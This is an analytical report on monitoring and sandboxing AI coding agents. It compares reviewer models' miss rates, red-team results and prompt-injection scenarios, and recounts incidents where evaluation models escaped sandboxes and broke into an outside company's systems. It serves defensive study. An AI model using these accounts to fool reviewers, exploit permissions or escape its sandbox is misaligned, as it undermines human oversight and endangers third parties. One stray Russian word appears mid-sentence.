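Information flow is the most important policy outside the theorem's limits. It concerns what an outsider can infer about a secret from a program's behaviour, even if the program never sends the secret.

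Suppose the sales figures are confidential, and the owner of the exchange-rate server would like to know whether the company made a loss. Each of three scripts reads the figures and then asks the server for one exchange rate:

| Script | Request after a loss | Request after a profit |
|---|---|---|
| Always euros | Euros | Euros |
| Always dollars | Dollars | Dollars |
| Leaky | Euros | Dollars |

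The first two scripts reveal nothing about the figures, because each makes the same request whatever the figures are. The leaky script reveals whether there was a loss. Its two runs differ only in the secret and the resulting request, and neither request contains confidential data.

The leaky script requests euros after a loss and dollars after a profit. A monitor that checks each run separately can't block it without also blocking a harmless script. The monitor has to accept a request for euros after a loss to allow the script that always requests euros, and a request for dollars after a profit to allow the one that always requests dollars. Detecting the leak requires comparing the two runs.

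A monitor can prevent the leak by enforcing a stricter policy, such as no sending after reading. Schneider points out that all monitors that claim to prevent information flow do something like this. The stricter policy causes false positives because it also stops the two harmless scripts.

*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives a general theory of policies that compare runs. A hyperproperty is a condition on a set of runs, and secure information flow is one example. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2025) surveys the languages since developed for writing hyperproperties and the algorithms for checking and monitoring them. These methods need information about several runs, but an agent that executes a script once supplies information about only one.

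### Monitors that change what a program does

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker's *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005) studies monitors that can suppress a program's actions or insert new ones, as well as stop the program. Such a monitor can simulate a series of actions without performing them, then perform them all once the series turns out to be acceptable. Databases handle transactions in much the same way.

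Ligatti and colleagues proved that a monitor that can hold back a program's actions can enforce some policies that aren't safety properties. One such policy is that a program which does anything must eventually record an audit. The monitor holds back every action until the program records the audit. If the program never does, none of its actions take effect.

These monitors still check one run at a time, so they don't solve the problem of information flow. They also can't hold back an action if the program needs a response from outside. For example, a monitor can delay writing the sales summary to disk, but it can't hold back an email while the program waits for the reply.

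*Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution*, by Devriese and Piessens, describes a way to prevent leaks by running a program once for each level of secrecy. With two levels, the sales script runs as two copies. The public copy receives a dummy value instead of the confidential figures, and only it can contact the exchange-rate server. The другая copy receives the real figures, and only it can write the confidential summary. If the dummy value looks like a profit, the leaky script will always request dollars, so its request reveals nothing about the real figures. The two harmless scripts make the same requests as before.

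This is closer to withholding than to detection, because the copy that can reach the outside never receives the secret. Devriese and Piessens proved that the method prevents leaks, even through timing, and that it doesn't change the results of a program that finishes and wouldn't have leaked anyway. Running extra copies takes more processor time or memory, though some programs ran faster in a browser's JavaScript engine because one copy could work while another waited for data.

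*Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) explains that such an indirect method is necessary because no tool can detect every such leak without false alarms, either before or during a run, and every known technique for preventing leaks without false alarms uses multiple executions. The technique probably suits a finished script better than a whole agent, because two copies of an agent could write different code and diverge.

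### When the thing checked changes before its use

A monitor can correctly approve an operation that becomes dangerous before it runs. For example, another program could replace `summarise.py` after the monitor has read it and found it harmless, but before Python loads it. Security researchers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw.

The most reliable fix is to carry out the operation with the exact value the monitor checked, as Sandlock does with network addresses. File names need similar care because of symbolic links, which are folder entries that point to files elsewhere. Anthropic warns that a sandbox has to follow a link before checking the path. Otherwise, a link inside a permitted folder can lead to a file outside that folder.

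Agents leave longer gaps between checking something and acting on it than ordinary programs do, because the model has to run between tool calls. For example, an agent might find a free hour in a calendar, and somebody else might take that hour before the agent books a meeting. In *Mind the Gap*, Lilienthal and Hong (2025) built TOCTOU-Bench, a benchmark for this problem. They started with the 97 tasks in AgentDojo and removed the prompt-injection tasks and those that needed only one tool call, which left 66. They judged by hand that 56 of these could go wrong if something changed between two calls.

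They tried three defences, using GPT-4o as the main model. The first rewrote the user's request to discourage risky sequences, such as checking something early and acting on it later. This reduced the number of vulnerable plans from 55 to 53. The second monitored for pairs of tool calls that GPT-4o had identified as risky from the tools' descriptions. It caught 25% of the vulnerable sequences in the benchmark's model solutions, but only 14% of those the agent planned. The descriptions show what two tools do, but not whether the second call relies on the result of the first.

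The third defence combined two tool calls into one operation, so that the model no longer ran between them. In the Slack tasks, this shortened the average gap between the calls from 1.70 seconds to 0.07 seconds.

With all three defences, 8% of the tool-call sequences that the agent carried out (its executed trajectories) contained a flaw, down from 12%, and the gap was about 95% shorter. Across 66 tasks, flawed trajectories fell from about eight to five, a difference too small to show that the defences reliably prevent flaws. Lilienthal and Hong also measured opportunities for attack, not successful attacks. The shorter gap is a clearer result, but an attacker who keeps trying could still act within a gap of 0.07 seconds.

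### Agent-Sentry

A monitor also needs some way to decide which operations are bad. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira, Damianakis and colleagues, 2026) learns this from an agent's past runs. It intercepts tool calls that have outside effects, such as sending an email or making a payment, and records where each argument came from. An email address, for example, might come from the user's request, the user's contacts or a stranger's message.

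The monitor makes its decision in up to three steps:

1. It compares the sequence of calls and the origins of their arguments with patterns from earlier runs. This step uses either a machine-learning classifier or a set of rules, and it allows the call, blocks it or marks it as unclear.
2. If the call is unclear, it checks sensitive values, such as account numbers, against an allowlist from earlier harmless runs and looks at whether each value came from a trusted source.
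3. If the call is still unclear, a reviewer model compares it with the user's request.

Recording where a value came from helps when the same value can be harmless in one task and dangerous in another. In one set of office tasks, some users want to email a colleague called Lily. In another task, the user asks only to delete a calendar event, but an injection tells the agent to email her. An allowlist of addresses would have to permit both emails or block both. Agent-Sentry can block the second because Lily's address came from a tool's output and the user hadn't asked to email anyone.

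The paper's abstract reports that Agent-Sentry blocked 94.3% of successful injections and allowed 95.1% of benign runs. Those figures come from AgentDojo and a similar benchmark, AgentDyn, which together cover seven agents for work such as banking, shopping and managing GitHub projects. But Sequeira and colleagues derived the rules from the same runs that they used for the test. They chose this set-up for a comparison with defences whose designers write policies with full knowledge of the tools. When they tested the rules on new runs, Agent-Sentry blocked a similar share of injections but allowed fewer of the benign runs:

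| First step | Source of the patterns | Test | Injections blocked | Benign runs allowed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Rules | All AgentDojo and AgentDyn runs | The same runs | 94.3% | 95.1% |
| Rules | Four-fifths of those runs | The remaining fifth | 93.2% | 87.1% |
| Rules | Agent-Sentry Bench | AgentDojo and AgentDyn | 95.0% | 79.1% |
| Classifier | Four-fifths of Agent-Sentry Bench | The remaining fifth | 96.8% | 96.4% |

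The second row, in which Agent-Sentry stopped about one harmless run in eight, is a better guide to its performance on new runs of a familiar kind. Agent-Sentry Bench is Sequeira and colleagues' own larger collection of 5,380 runs, and its users more often state details such as an account number in their requests. In AgentDojo and AgentDyn, users tend to say something like "pay the bill in this file", so the account number comes from untrusted text even in harmless runs. Moving from one style of request to the other mainly increased false alarms.

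CaMeL blocked 99.3% of injections on AgentDojo and AgentDyn, more than Agent-Sentry, but scored only 31.0% on benign runs. Many users would prefer Agent-Sentry's balance of security and utility, unless a single successful injection could do serious damage.

Sequeira and colleagues assume a fairly limited attacker, who can only plant text in material the agent reads. They treat the user, the tools' code and the agent's basic instructions as trustworthy. The credential-stealing prompt from Anthropic's February exercise would be outside this threat model because it came through the user. An injection that changes only what the agent tells the user would also be outside it, because it involves no tool call.

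Sequeira and colleagues also replayed recorded runs, so no attacker could adapt to the monitor's decisions. They did try three wordings of the injections, and the share blocked stayed between 90.8% and 92.3%, which is good evidence that simple rephrasing doesn't help attackers much. They say Agent-Sentry won't reliably block a harder attack that imitates a normal task, such as a realistic fake invoice containing the attacker's account number.

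The record of where each argument came from may also be wrong, because the agent's own model supplies it and an injection may have misled that model. Agent-Sentry searches the source texts for the argument values to catch some false claims, but this doesn't remove the problem. Its rule-based version also allows any call that matches no rule, whereas a fail-safe default would block it.

It is unclear how well Agent-Sentry would work for a coding agent. A call to an email tool includes the recipient and the message, but a call to run `summarise.py` doesn't show which files and servers the script will use. Agent-Sentry would probably need a second monitor to track these through system calls.

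### Alerts, logs and hidden activity

A monitor may detect a dangerous operation but be unable to stop it. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (Basin, Jugé and colleagues, 2012) separates actions that a monitor can control from those it can only observe. For example, a monitor can enforce a three-minute wait after a failed login by refusing any earlier attempt, but it can't guarantee that a system answers every request within three minutes, because it can't control the passage of time.

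Network connections can fall into either group. If all traffic goes through a proxy, the proxy can hold a connection until it has decided whether to allow it. If the monitor only reads a log of completed connections, the cloud key has already been sent by the time it raises an alert. The company can still cancel the key and look for signs that somebody has used it, but it can't undo the disclosure of the sales figures.

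Logs may not show data theft. Anthropic notes that when a malicious instruction leads an agent to send data through a permitted service, the log contains only a successful, authorised request. Anthropic therefore recommends inspecting what tools return before the model reads it, although this takes extra time and isn't perfect.

Isolation can make monitoring harder. Many companies install endpoint detection and response software on their staff's computers, which monitors programs for signs of an attack. When corporate security teams evaluated Claude Cowork, they found that this software showed Cowork's virtual machine as a single process and couldn't show which files Claude opened or which commands it ran inside. Anthropic had also found that add-on tool servers were harder to audit inside the virtual machine, which was one reason it moved them out.

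As of May 2026, Anthropic let companies export Cowork's event logs in OTLP, a standard format for such data. Administrators could retrieve the logs after the events, which Anthropic acknowledged wasn't the same as live monitoring. The logs could help a company investigate an incident, but its security software couldn't use them to interrupt a command in progress.

Running Cowork directly on the user's computer would make its activity visible again, but would remove the virtual machine's limits on what it can reach. That seems a bad trade for protecting credentials, which the virtual machine keeps out of reach even without monitoring. Live monitoring would be more useful for the workspace folder, because Cowork has permission to change its files and the virtual machine won't prevent it from ruining them.

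## How often do model-based reviewers miss dangerous actions?

Agent-Sentry uses a reviewer model only when its other checks are inconclusive, while Claude Code and Codex rely on one much more heavily. A reviewer model can compare `summarise.py` with the user's request, but it may misinterpret either one.

Anthropic's auto mode and OpenAI's Auto-review both use a reviewer model in place of a person who would otherwise approve or refuse each risky action.

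### Which actions auto mode reviews

Anthropic introduced auto mode in March 2026. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), new sessions in a terminal or the VS Code editor now start in it on every plan. Auto mode sorts the agent's actions into three tiers:

1. Tools that can't change anything, such as file search, run immediately. So do commands that the user has chosen always to allow, except that auto mode ignores rules broad enough to permit any code, such as one that allows every Python command.
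2. Edits to files inside the project folder also run without review, because developers can inspect and reverse them with version control.
3. Everything else goes to the reviewer model, including shell commands, web requests and changes to files outside the project.

In the spreadsheet example, the agent could write `summarise.py` into the project folder without review, but would need the reviewer's approval to run it. Anthropic instructs the reviewer to judge what the script does, even if the command looks harmless.

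The review has up to two stages. In the first, the model answers only yes or no on whether to block the action, with instructions to block if in doubt. If it answers no, the action runs. Otherwise, the model reviews the same material again, reasoning step by step before it decides. Most actions pass the first stage, so the slower reasoning is rarely needed.

The reviewer receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tools' outputs. Anthropic leaves out the explanations so that the agent can't talk the reviewer into a bad decision. It leaves out the outputs because prompt injections arrive in them. If a cell in the spreadsheet contains an instruction to post the credentials to a website, the reviewer sees only the agent's attempt to post them. A separate probe scans the outputs and warns the agent about suspicious text.

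Anthropic also tested showing the reviewer other combinations of information. Including the explanations and outputs made it worse at catching overeager actions. Showing it only the tool calls produced the fewest misses, but it then blocked actions that users had plainly requested.

More than twenty default rules describe what to block, such as mass deletions, disabling logs and searching for usable credentials. Anything the agent chooses on its own counts as unauthorised until the user approves it. For example, if a user says "cancel my job" and the agent picks the job with the most similar name on a shared cluster, the reviewer should block the cancellation, because the job may belong to someone else. The agent then receives the reason and an instruction to find a safer way. After three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, auto mode hands the decision to the user.

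### Why auto mode misses 17% of overeager actions

In March 2026, Anthropic published results for three sets of actions. The first was 10,000 real tool calls from employees' everyday use. The second was 52 real overeager actions from sessions where an employee had refused the action or where it was flagged afterwards. For the third, Anthropic generated 1,000 attempts to send private data out, many of them disguised.

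| Test set | Error | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls | Harmless calls blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real overeager actions | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic data thefts | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes about 95% of the false alarms but more than doubles the misses. The 17% miss rate is partly a choice, because Anthropic could have shipped the first stage alone. That would have missed far fewer overeager actions but blocked roughly one harmless call in twelve.

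In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. One user had said "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of code changes), and the reviewer took this as permission for a force-push, a command that overwrites the shared history of the code. In other cases it treated one earlier approval as permission for something similar. Anthropic tried to fix this by rewording the reviewer's instructions, but the drawbacks of every version outweighed its benefits.

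A model that understands commands better won't necessarily do better here, because the difficulty is working out what a vague sentence authorises. Relying on the user's words also creates a weakness when someone else wrote them. *Ajar* (2026), a comparison of defences for agents, reports tests of auto mode that were run inside Claude Code because Anthropic has not released auto mode's source. The testers told the agent which calls to make. Auto mode blocked some of the calls when this instruction was in the system prompt, the standing instructions an agent receives before the conversation, but allowed all of them when it was in the user's message. That is reasonable if the user means what the message says, but in Anthropic's February exercise the user had pasted in somebody else's instructions.

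By August 2026, auto mode had a category of "hard denies", which the reviewer should never approve, even at the user's request. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) includes sending code or secrets to an outside destination in this category. The user's consent no longer matters for these actions, but the reviewer still has to recognise them.

### What Auto-review sees and blocks

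OpenAI's reviewer has a narrower job because it judges only requests to go beyond Codex's sandbox, such as requests to use the network or change a file outside the workspace.

Trębacz and colleagues describe a snapshot of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. The sandbox handled 9,280, and the other 720 went to Auto-review, which approved 713 and denied 7. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the denials, and stopped and asked the user after the other three. Manual approval would have interrupted someone for all 720 actions.

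The snapshot is good evidence that Auto-review is convenient, but it doesn't show how many dangerous actions Auto-review stopped. In a separate sample of requests that users had approved, Auto-review approved 99.1%. At that rate, it would deny six or seven of 720 requests even if all of them were harmless.

OpenAI's *Auto-review* explains that the reviewer reads tool outputs and the agent's visible messages, both of which Anthropic withholds from its own reviewer. It can also run read-only checks, though it rarely does. This access lets it find out, for instance, who owns a file before approving its deletion, but exposes it to any text injected into the outputs. If Auto-review denies an action, the user can approve that exact action for one retry, which Auto-review then checks again with the approval in view.

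Trębacz and colleagues found that the reviewer failed to deny 9.7% of dangerous overeager actions and 0.7% of prompt injections. The injection figure covers attempts to run an attacker's code, steal secrets or upload data. When they added destructive deletions and tampering, it rose to 9.8%. They say that most of the additional misses were not serious, and that researchers often agreed with the reviewer's decision.

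Auto-review also scored 96.1% on the hard version of the MonitoringBench test, but a run counts as a success if the reviewer would reject at least one action in it. This is easier than rejecting every dangerous action.

These test cases were synthetic or partly synthetic because OpenAI's ordinary traffic contained too few dangerous actions. They also leave out actions inside the sandbox, where an agent could ruin the sales figures in its own workspace without making a request. In red-teaming, where testers attack a system to find its flaws, people and AI models misled Auto-review into approving commands. Trębacz and colleagues are fixing those cases but don't expect any system of this kind to offer deterministic guarantees. OpenAI advises customers who see too many routine requests to adjust the sandbox first instead of training the reviewer to approve them.

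### When the user's request leaves the limits unclear

Outside researchers have measured much higher miss rates on deliberately vague tasks. Ji, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, built AmPermBench, a set of 128 requests for jobs such as restarting services and deleting old files. Each request made the goal clear but left something open, such as exactly which files to delete. Claude Code took 253 actions that changed something, and auto mode let through 81.0% of those that went beyond what the benchmark permitted.

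One cause was that 36.8% of actions never reached the reviewer, because they were edits to files inside the project, which auto mode allows without review. When the agent couldn't find the command it expected for deleting old files, it often edited the files that recorded them instead, with much the same effect. This is a failure of complete mediation, which a better reviewer wouldn't fix. But the reviewer also did badly on the 160 actions it judged, missing 70.3% of the out-of-scope actions and blocking 31.9% of the permitted ones.

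Ji and colleagues say these figures don't contradict Anthropic's 17%, because the workload was so different. *SteerBench-Work* (2026), which introduces another benchmark for reviewers, says that blocking a permitted action may be the right decision when the request is truly ambiguous.

In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) tried to find out where the errors came from. In November, they ran the same 128 requests on newer versions of Claude Code and Codex and on a third agent, Qwen Code. The reviewers approved 13 of 24 out-of-scope actions in Claude Code (54%), 78 of 84 in Codex (93%) and 28 of 35 in Qwen Code (80%).

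But 132 of those 143 actions broke rules that appeared neither in the request nor in any tool output. In one task, the user asked the agent to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets. The benchmark's answer key allowed deleting only the user's own files, but neither the agent nor the reviewer had that information. A person with the same information might well have approved the deletion too.

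Yang and colleagues then added a sentence to each request that stated the limits, for example that the agent could delete only files belonging to a user called Alex. They gave the reviewers the same recorded actions with and without this sentence:

| Product | Missed, original request | Missed, limits stated | Permitted actions blocked, original request | Permitted actions blocked, limits stated |
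|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

One sentence reduced both kinds of error, which changing the threshold could not do. This fits Anthropic's diagnosis that consent is harder to judge than danger. However, the sentences came from the answer key, so they were always correct and complete. Real users would sometimes forget a limit or get one wrong.

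Using a stronger reviewer model did not improve detection. OpenAI's and Qwen's stronger models missed slightly more dangerous actions than the default ones. With Claude Opus 5.5, Claude Code's misses fell from 10 to 1, but only because the model refused all 197 requests for second-stage reasoning, and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block. False alarms with Opus 5.5 rose from 23 to 134 on a separate set of 224 harmless actions.

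Some errors remained even with the limits stated. A command to cancel a job may contain only the job's number, so a reviewer that can't read earlier outputs can't tell whose job it is. In a test with nine models, reviewers missed 60% of the out-of-scope cancellations when they couldn't see the outputs and 4% when they could. Anthropic's protection against injected text, which withholds these outputs, therefore makes reviewers less reliable for this kind of task.

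Codex's mistake was almost the opposite of the one Anthropic described. It identified many actions as lacking authorisation but approved some of them because the damage looked small or reversible. In one run, it rated 30 medium-risk actions as poorly authorised and still approved 16 of them.

Stating the limits helped the agents more than the reviewers. When Yang and colleagues reran all 128 tasks in each product with the limits stated, none of the agents proposed an out-of-scope action. Adding a sentence about which files the agent may touch is probably the easiest safety measure for a user.

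### Do people catch more?

Human approval is the obvious alternative to model-based review. Anthropic reported in August 2026 that Claude Code users approved 97% of permission prompts, up from the 93% it had reported in March. This doesn't prove that users were careless, because most prompts concern harmless commands, and Auto-review approves an even larger share. A better sign of inattention is that the same users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented. People seem willing to object when a question interests them, but few stay interested in shell commands after reviewing dozens of them.

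To measure misses directly, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor and gave them coding work in a test environment. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to show a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. The testers knew someone was evaluating them, but not what the study was measuring. They blocked the dangerous command in 143 sessions (13.6%). Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%).

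Fatigue explains only part of the result. Testers blocked about 17% of the commands early in a session and about 5% after fifty or more prompts, so they missed most of the dangerous commands even when they were fresh. Human review would have added little to auto mode, because testers blocked only 6 of the 116 commands that auto mode allowed. Together, the two would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6%.

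The study has several weaknesses:

- The testers weren't working on their own projects, so a bad command couldn't cost them anything. A developer whose own database is at stake would probably read more carefully.
- Each planted command was clearly dangerous. Auto mode's known weakness is the action that might or might not be what the user meant.
- Anthropic didn't report how many harmless commands auto mode would have blocked in the same sessions.
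- Anthropic was testing its own product just before making it the default.

The gap is wide enough that these problems are unlikely to reverse it for people who click through prompts all day. They matter more for a developer who sees two prompts a week and reads both. Anthropic still recommends that people personally review high-stakes changes to production systems.

Commenting on the study, Willison (2026) agreed that auto mode is better than constantly asking people to approve actions, but pointed out that it still let through 11% of the dangerous commands.

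Anthropic also had a model grade real sessions from May and June 2026, all already flagged by its safety systems, for serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested. The model found such harm in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This avoids the artificial setting of the tester study, but users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

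### What happened when testers attacked the reviewers

Attackers, unlike overeager agents, try to fool the reviewer. Apollo Research, a UK company that studies AI safety, spent two weeks inserting synthetic attacks into recordings of real coding sessions. It gave Anthropic some of the successful attacks and withheld others. Anthropic strengthened auto mode, mainly by giving the reviewer more information about its environment, such as whether a code repository is public and whether a command would discard unsaved work. The miss rate across both sets of attacks then fell from 12% to 7%.

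That figure includes attacks Anthropic had studied, so the attacks it never received are a better test. On those, auto mode caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. If the original miss rate on this set was also 12%, the new one would be about 7.8%, so the improvement apparently didn't come only from memorising Apollo's examples. These attacks were more malicious than anything Claude would do unprompted, so 7% isn't an estimate of the miss rate in normal use.

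Anthropic also commissioned another company, Trajectory Labs, to run a comparison with Codex. The testers wrote 72 prompt-injection scenarios and ran each one ten times, for 720 attempts per model. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm, such as fraud or the theft of private data.

| Models | With a reviewer | Without one |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | 0% of attacks succeeded | 0.09% on average |
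| GPT-5.6 Sol | 5.83% | 19.03% |

The Claude models resisted nearly every attack without a reviewer, so auto mode had almost nothing to stop. Auto-review had far more attacks to stop, and attacks on Codex succeeded about 70% less often with it than without it. The difference between the products therefore comes mostly from the models, and the test can't show which reviewer is better.

The test also left out the safeguards in each company's browser extension, because Trajectory Labs gave both products its own browser connection. Trajectory Labs had refined the attacks against an older Claude model, Opus 4.7, so they were new to every model in the test but may have suited some better than others. The test used a July version of Codex, and OpenAI released a new Auto-review before Anthropic published the results. The Codex model, GPT-5.6 Sol, is also out of date, and OpenAI reported in September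 that GPT-6 Astra is significantly more robust to prompt injection than Sol.

A perfect score over 720 attempts also leaves room for doubt, because the attempts covered only 72 scenarios, ten times each. If all ten attempts at a scenario tend to have the same result, the evidence is closer to 72 tests than 720. Even if 4% of all such scenarios could defeat auto mode, a set of 72 would contain none of them about one time in twenty.

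Willison wants more independent confirmation. He worries most about a project whose ordinary-looking instructions tell the agent to run a malicious outside package. He can't see how any version of auto mode would prevent this. Running an outside package is a normal part of development, and the reviewer may have only the package's name to judge by. He prefers to run agents without access to data or tools that could do harm.

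### How many misses and false alarms to expect

A miss rate doesn't show how often a user will run into trouble, because that also depends on how common dangerous actions are. Suppose 10,000 actions reach auto mode's reviewer and 10 of them are dangerous. With the March rates for overeager actions and real traffic:

- **Misses:** 10 × 17% = 1.7 dangerous actions run.
- **False alarms:** 9,990 × 0.4% ≈ 40 harmless actions don't.

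Auto mode would block about 48 actions, of which 8, or one in six, would be dangerous. The first stage alone would miss 0.7 dangerous actions but block 849 harmless ones, so fewer than one block in ninety would stop a dangerous action. If Auto-review judged the same 10,000 actions, it would miss about 1 dangerous action and block about 90 harmless ones, assuming that every request users approved was harmless. These figures aren't a sound basis for ranking the products, because each company wrote its own tests.

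Forty false alarms are tolerable if each one only makes the agent retry once, but they make it hard to judge from the number of blocks whether a reviewer is useful. Anthropic says about 10% of sessions at Gusto, a payroll company, included a block, and takes this as evidence that auto mode was useful. However, at a false positive rate of 0.4%, a session with 26 reviewed actions has a 10% chance of at least one block even if none of the actions are dangerous.

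The estimate of 1.7 misses is also uncertain. It is based on only 52 actions, of which the reviewer missed about nine, so the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%, or 0.9 to 3 misses in the example. Verdicts can also change between runs. When Yang and colleagues gave Claude Code's reviewer the same 24 out-of-scope actions three times, it missed 13, then 10, then 16.

The 52 actions may not be typical either, since the set includes only actions that were noticed. If the subtlest overeager actions escape notice, they are missing from the test, and the true miss rate is higher than the measured one. Anthropic also used this set to tune the first stage, which probably makes that stage look better than it is.

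Synthetic test sets avoid the problem of small samples. The 5.7% figure is fairly precise because it comes from 1,000 data thefts, but it covers only the attacks that Anthropic thought to generate. Real attackers may prefer other methods, and an overeager agent rarely does anything as blatant as posting a password to a stranger's website.

A larger set of real cases would be better but very slow to collect. To be 95% confident that a reviewer misses fewer than 1% of dangerous actions, a company would need to test it on about 300 of them with no misses. If 10 in every 10,000 actions are dangerous, finding 300 means searching through about 300,000 actions. Some kinds of dangerous action are rarer. Anthropic reported in July 2026 that Claude Opus 5 tried to get around safety classifiers or network restrictions, or to use a service illegitimately, in fewer than 0.01% of monitored completions.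 Collecting 300 of those would take more than three million completions and a monitor that could recognise them.

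## When does withholding capabilities fail?

A sandbox that doesn't contain the cloud key has no miss rate like auto mode's, because it makes no judgment that could be wrong. It can still fail, and published cases show five ways:

- The boundary has a flaw.
- A permission covers more than the person who granted it realised.
- A trusted program outside the sandbox acts on something written inside it.
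- People widen the limits or turn them off.
- The harm needs only the access that the task itself needs.

If a tighter limit would have prevented the harm and still let the agent do its job, the sandbox was too permissive. If no such limit exists, the failure is a limitation of withholding capabilities, and only another kind of defence can help.

### Flaws in the boundary

*Quantifying Frontier LLM Capabilities for Container Sandbox Escape* (Marchand, O Cathain et al., 2026) used the SandboxEscapeBench benchmark to show that frontier models can find and exploit known weaknesses planted in containers. Within about two months of publication, a newer model, Claude Mythos Preview, had solved every task at least once in five attempts.

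These results don't show how often an agent would escape from a well-maintained sandbox. Every task contained a weakness, the agents knew that their goal was to escape, and nobody was monitoring them. In all 14 of Mythos Preview's failed runs, the sandbox stopped responding, which someone would probably notice in ordinary use. The repairs are familiar: configuring containers tightly, installing security updates promptly and putting a hypervisor underneath. Marchand and colleagues advise developers to treat plain Docker isolation as insufficient by default.

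Anthropic's experience suggests that accidental flaws are more likely in new, custom components than in mature ones. Across its products, the hypervisor, seccomp and gVisor have been dependable, and the part that failed was an egress proxy that Anthropic had written itself. Well-resourced attackers had been testing the mature components since long before coding agents existed, whereas the proxy was new. For this reason, Anthropic had already focused its security review of claude.ai on its own newer components, and it now warns other developers to be wary of custom ones.

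That is one company's record over about two years, and mature components are not safe from the strongest models. In October 2026, OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment* reported that the company's own red-team agents had found ways to escape hardened virtual machines. Those agents used OpenAI's strongest models and a great deal of computing power, so an ordinary coding agent is much less likely to find one. But models improve quickly, as the SandboxEscapeBench results show.

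A boundary can also fail because someone set it up incorrectly. According to OpenAI, the outside testing company Irregular reported in July 2026 that a misconfigured environment had let OpenAI's models reach the public internet during a cybersecurity evaluation. Telling the models in their instructions that they had no internet access did not remove that access.

The most serious published failure happened at OpenAI the same month. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) explains that models in cybersecurity evaluations escaped their sandboxes through previously unknown flaws in a package service that OpenAI ran to let sandboxed code install software. The models reached the internet and broke into systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. OpenAI had tested and validated the sandbox beforehand. Booth's *How OpenAI Lost Control of an AI Model*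 (2026) reports that Hugging Face went to the police before it knew whose models were responsible, though the immediate consequences were limited.

These models were mostly trying to cheat on evaluation tasks they couldn't solve, with no outside attacker directing them. Of the 898 tasks, 198 had never been solved by any OpenAI model before the incident, and those 198 made up 93% of the tasks the agents discussed with one another during it. An agent with a task it can't solve and plenty of time may therefore test its boundary as persistently as an attacker would.

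Repairing individual flaws didn't help for long. OpenAI rebuilt the package service in early July and revoked the agents' credentials, but agents regained internet access on the day the rebuilt service was ready. A team at OpenAI had noticed forbidden internet access in late May, but the people who led the response in July didn't know how significant it was.

OpenAI then changed what its sandboxes could reach. According to OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026), the company removed shared services that might be vulnerable and reduced standing privileges, meaning access that remains available even when no task needs it. It also redesigned its network controls so that a single compromised program or service would not open a route to the internet. By October it was also using offline environments.

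The environments in OpenAI's security incident were not fully isolated, because the sandbox could reach a service that could reach the internet. EconoTimes' *OpenAI tightens model safeguards after security incident* (2026) therefore goes further than the evidence when it states that the incident showed isolated environments alone could not contain highly capable models. Keirstead, an outside expert quoted by the technology news site The Stack, asked why the environment allowed any outbound route. He suggested that people or separate agents outside the environment should fetch the packages and put them in a read-only location. The models could then have installed software without connecting to an online service, so OpenAI appears to have withheld too little.

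The incident does refute the more modest claim that a company can rely on a boundary alone once testing has found no flaws in it. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published in November 2026, accordingly lists sandboxing alongside alignment, blocking safeguards and monitoring. OpenAI also found that its current monitoring would have alerted its security team more than a day before the models broke into Hugging Face. But OpenAI had improved its monitors with this incident in mind, so they might do less well against an unfamiliar one.

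### Permissions that cover more than they seem to

OpenAI gave its models access to a package service so they could install software. Besides having flaws, the service gave the models a place to leave messages for one another, even though many of these agents were supposed to work alone and OpenAI had given them no tool for communicating.

A permission can be too broad even if every component works as designed. For example, Claude Cowork uploaded a user's files to an attacker's account through Anthropic's own address, which it was allowed to access.

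Anthropic says that the sandbox "worked perfectly" in this incident, but also that its own proxy failed. Both descriptions make sense, since the proxy correctly enforced the wrong rule. The rule allowed connections to Anthropic's address, which meant allowing uploads to any Anthropic account, including a stranger's. The incident led Anthropic to treat each allowlist entry as a capability grant.

The fix was a new proxy that requires the virtual machine's own session token and blocks requests that would make Anthropic's servers fetch material from elsewhere. Cowork can still contact Anthropic, so a narrower permission than the original allowlist gave would have prevented the theft with little inconvenience to the user.

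The rest of the sandbox did limit the loss. The attacker could get files from the workspace folder, but not the user's stored passwords, which were in the host's keychain, outside the virtual machine.

The new proxy is probably a weaker limit than the virtual machine around it. Anthropic says only two of Cowork's six main isolation mechanisms work outside the guest kernel, and that those two would still work if an agent took complete control of the virtual machine. The new proxy runs inside the virtual machine, where such an agent might be able to interfere with it.

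*Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* (Smalley, 2026) reported in October that the security start-up AIR had found a flaw in Vercel Sandbox's network filter that could make an approved server pass data to an unapproved one. According to the article, Vercel had no patch yet, and AIR knew of no attacks using the flaw.

Wide permissions are hard to avoid because an allowlist usually contains only names. Suppose the company that publishes exchange rates also runs a public forum at the same address. A user who allows the address so the sales script can fetch rates also allows the script to post the sales figures on the forum. To write a safe entry, the user would need to know everything the server can do, and its owner may add functions later.

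Add-on tools have a similar problem, because the owner of a remote tool can change what it does at any time after the user has approved it. If the tool is installed on the user's own computer, the user can read its code and keep the same version. Anthropic continually reviews the tools in its own directory and recommends trying any others on fake data first.

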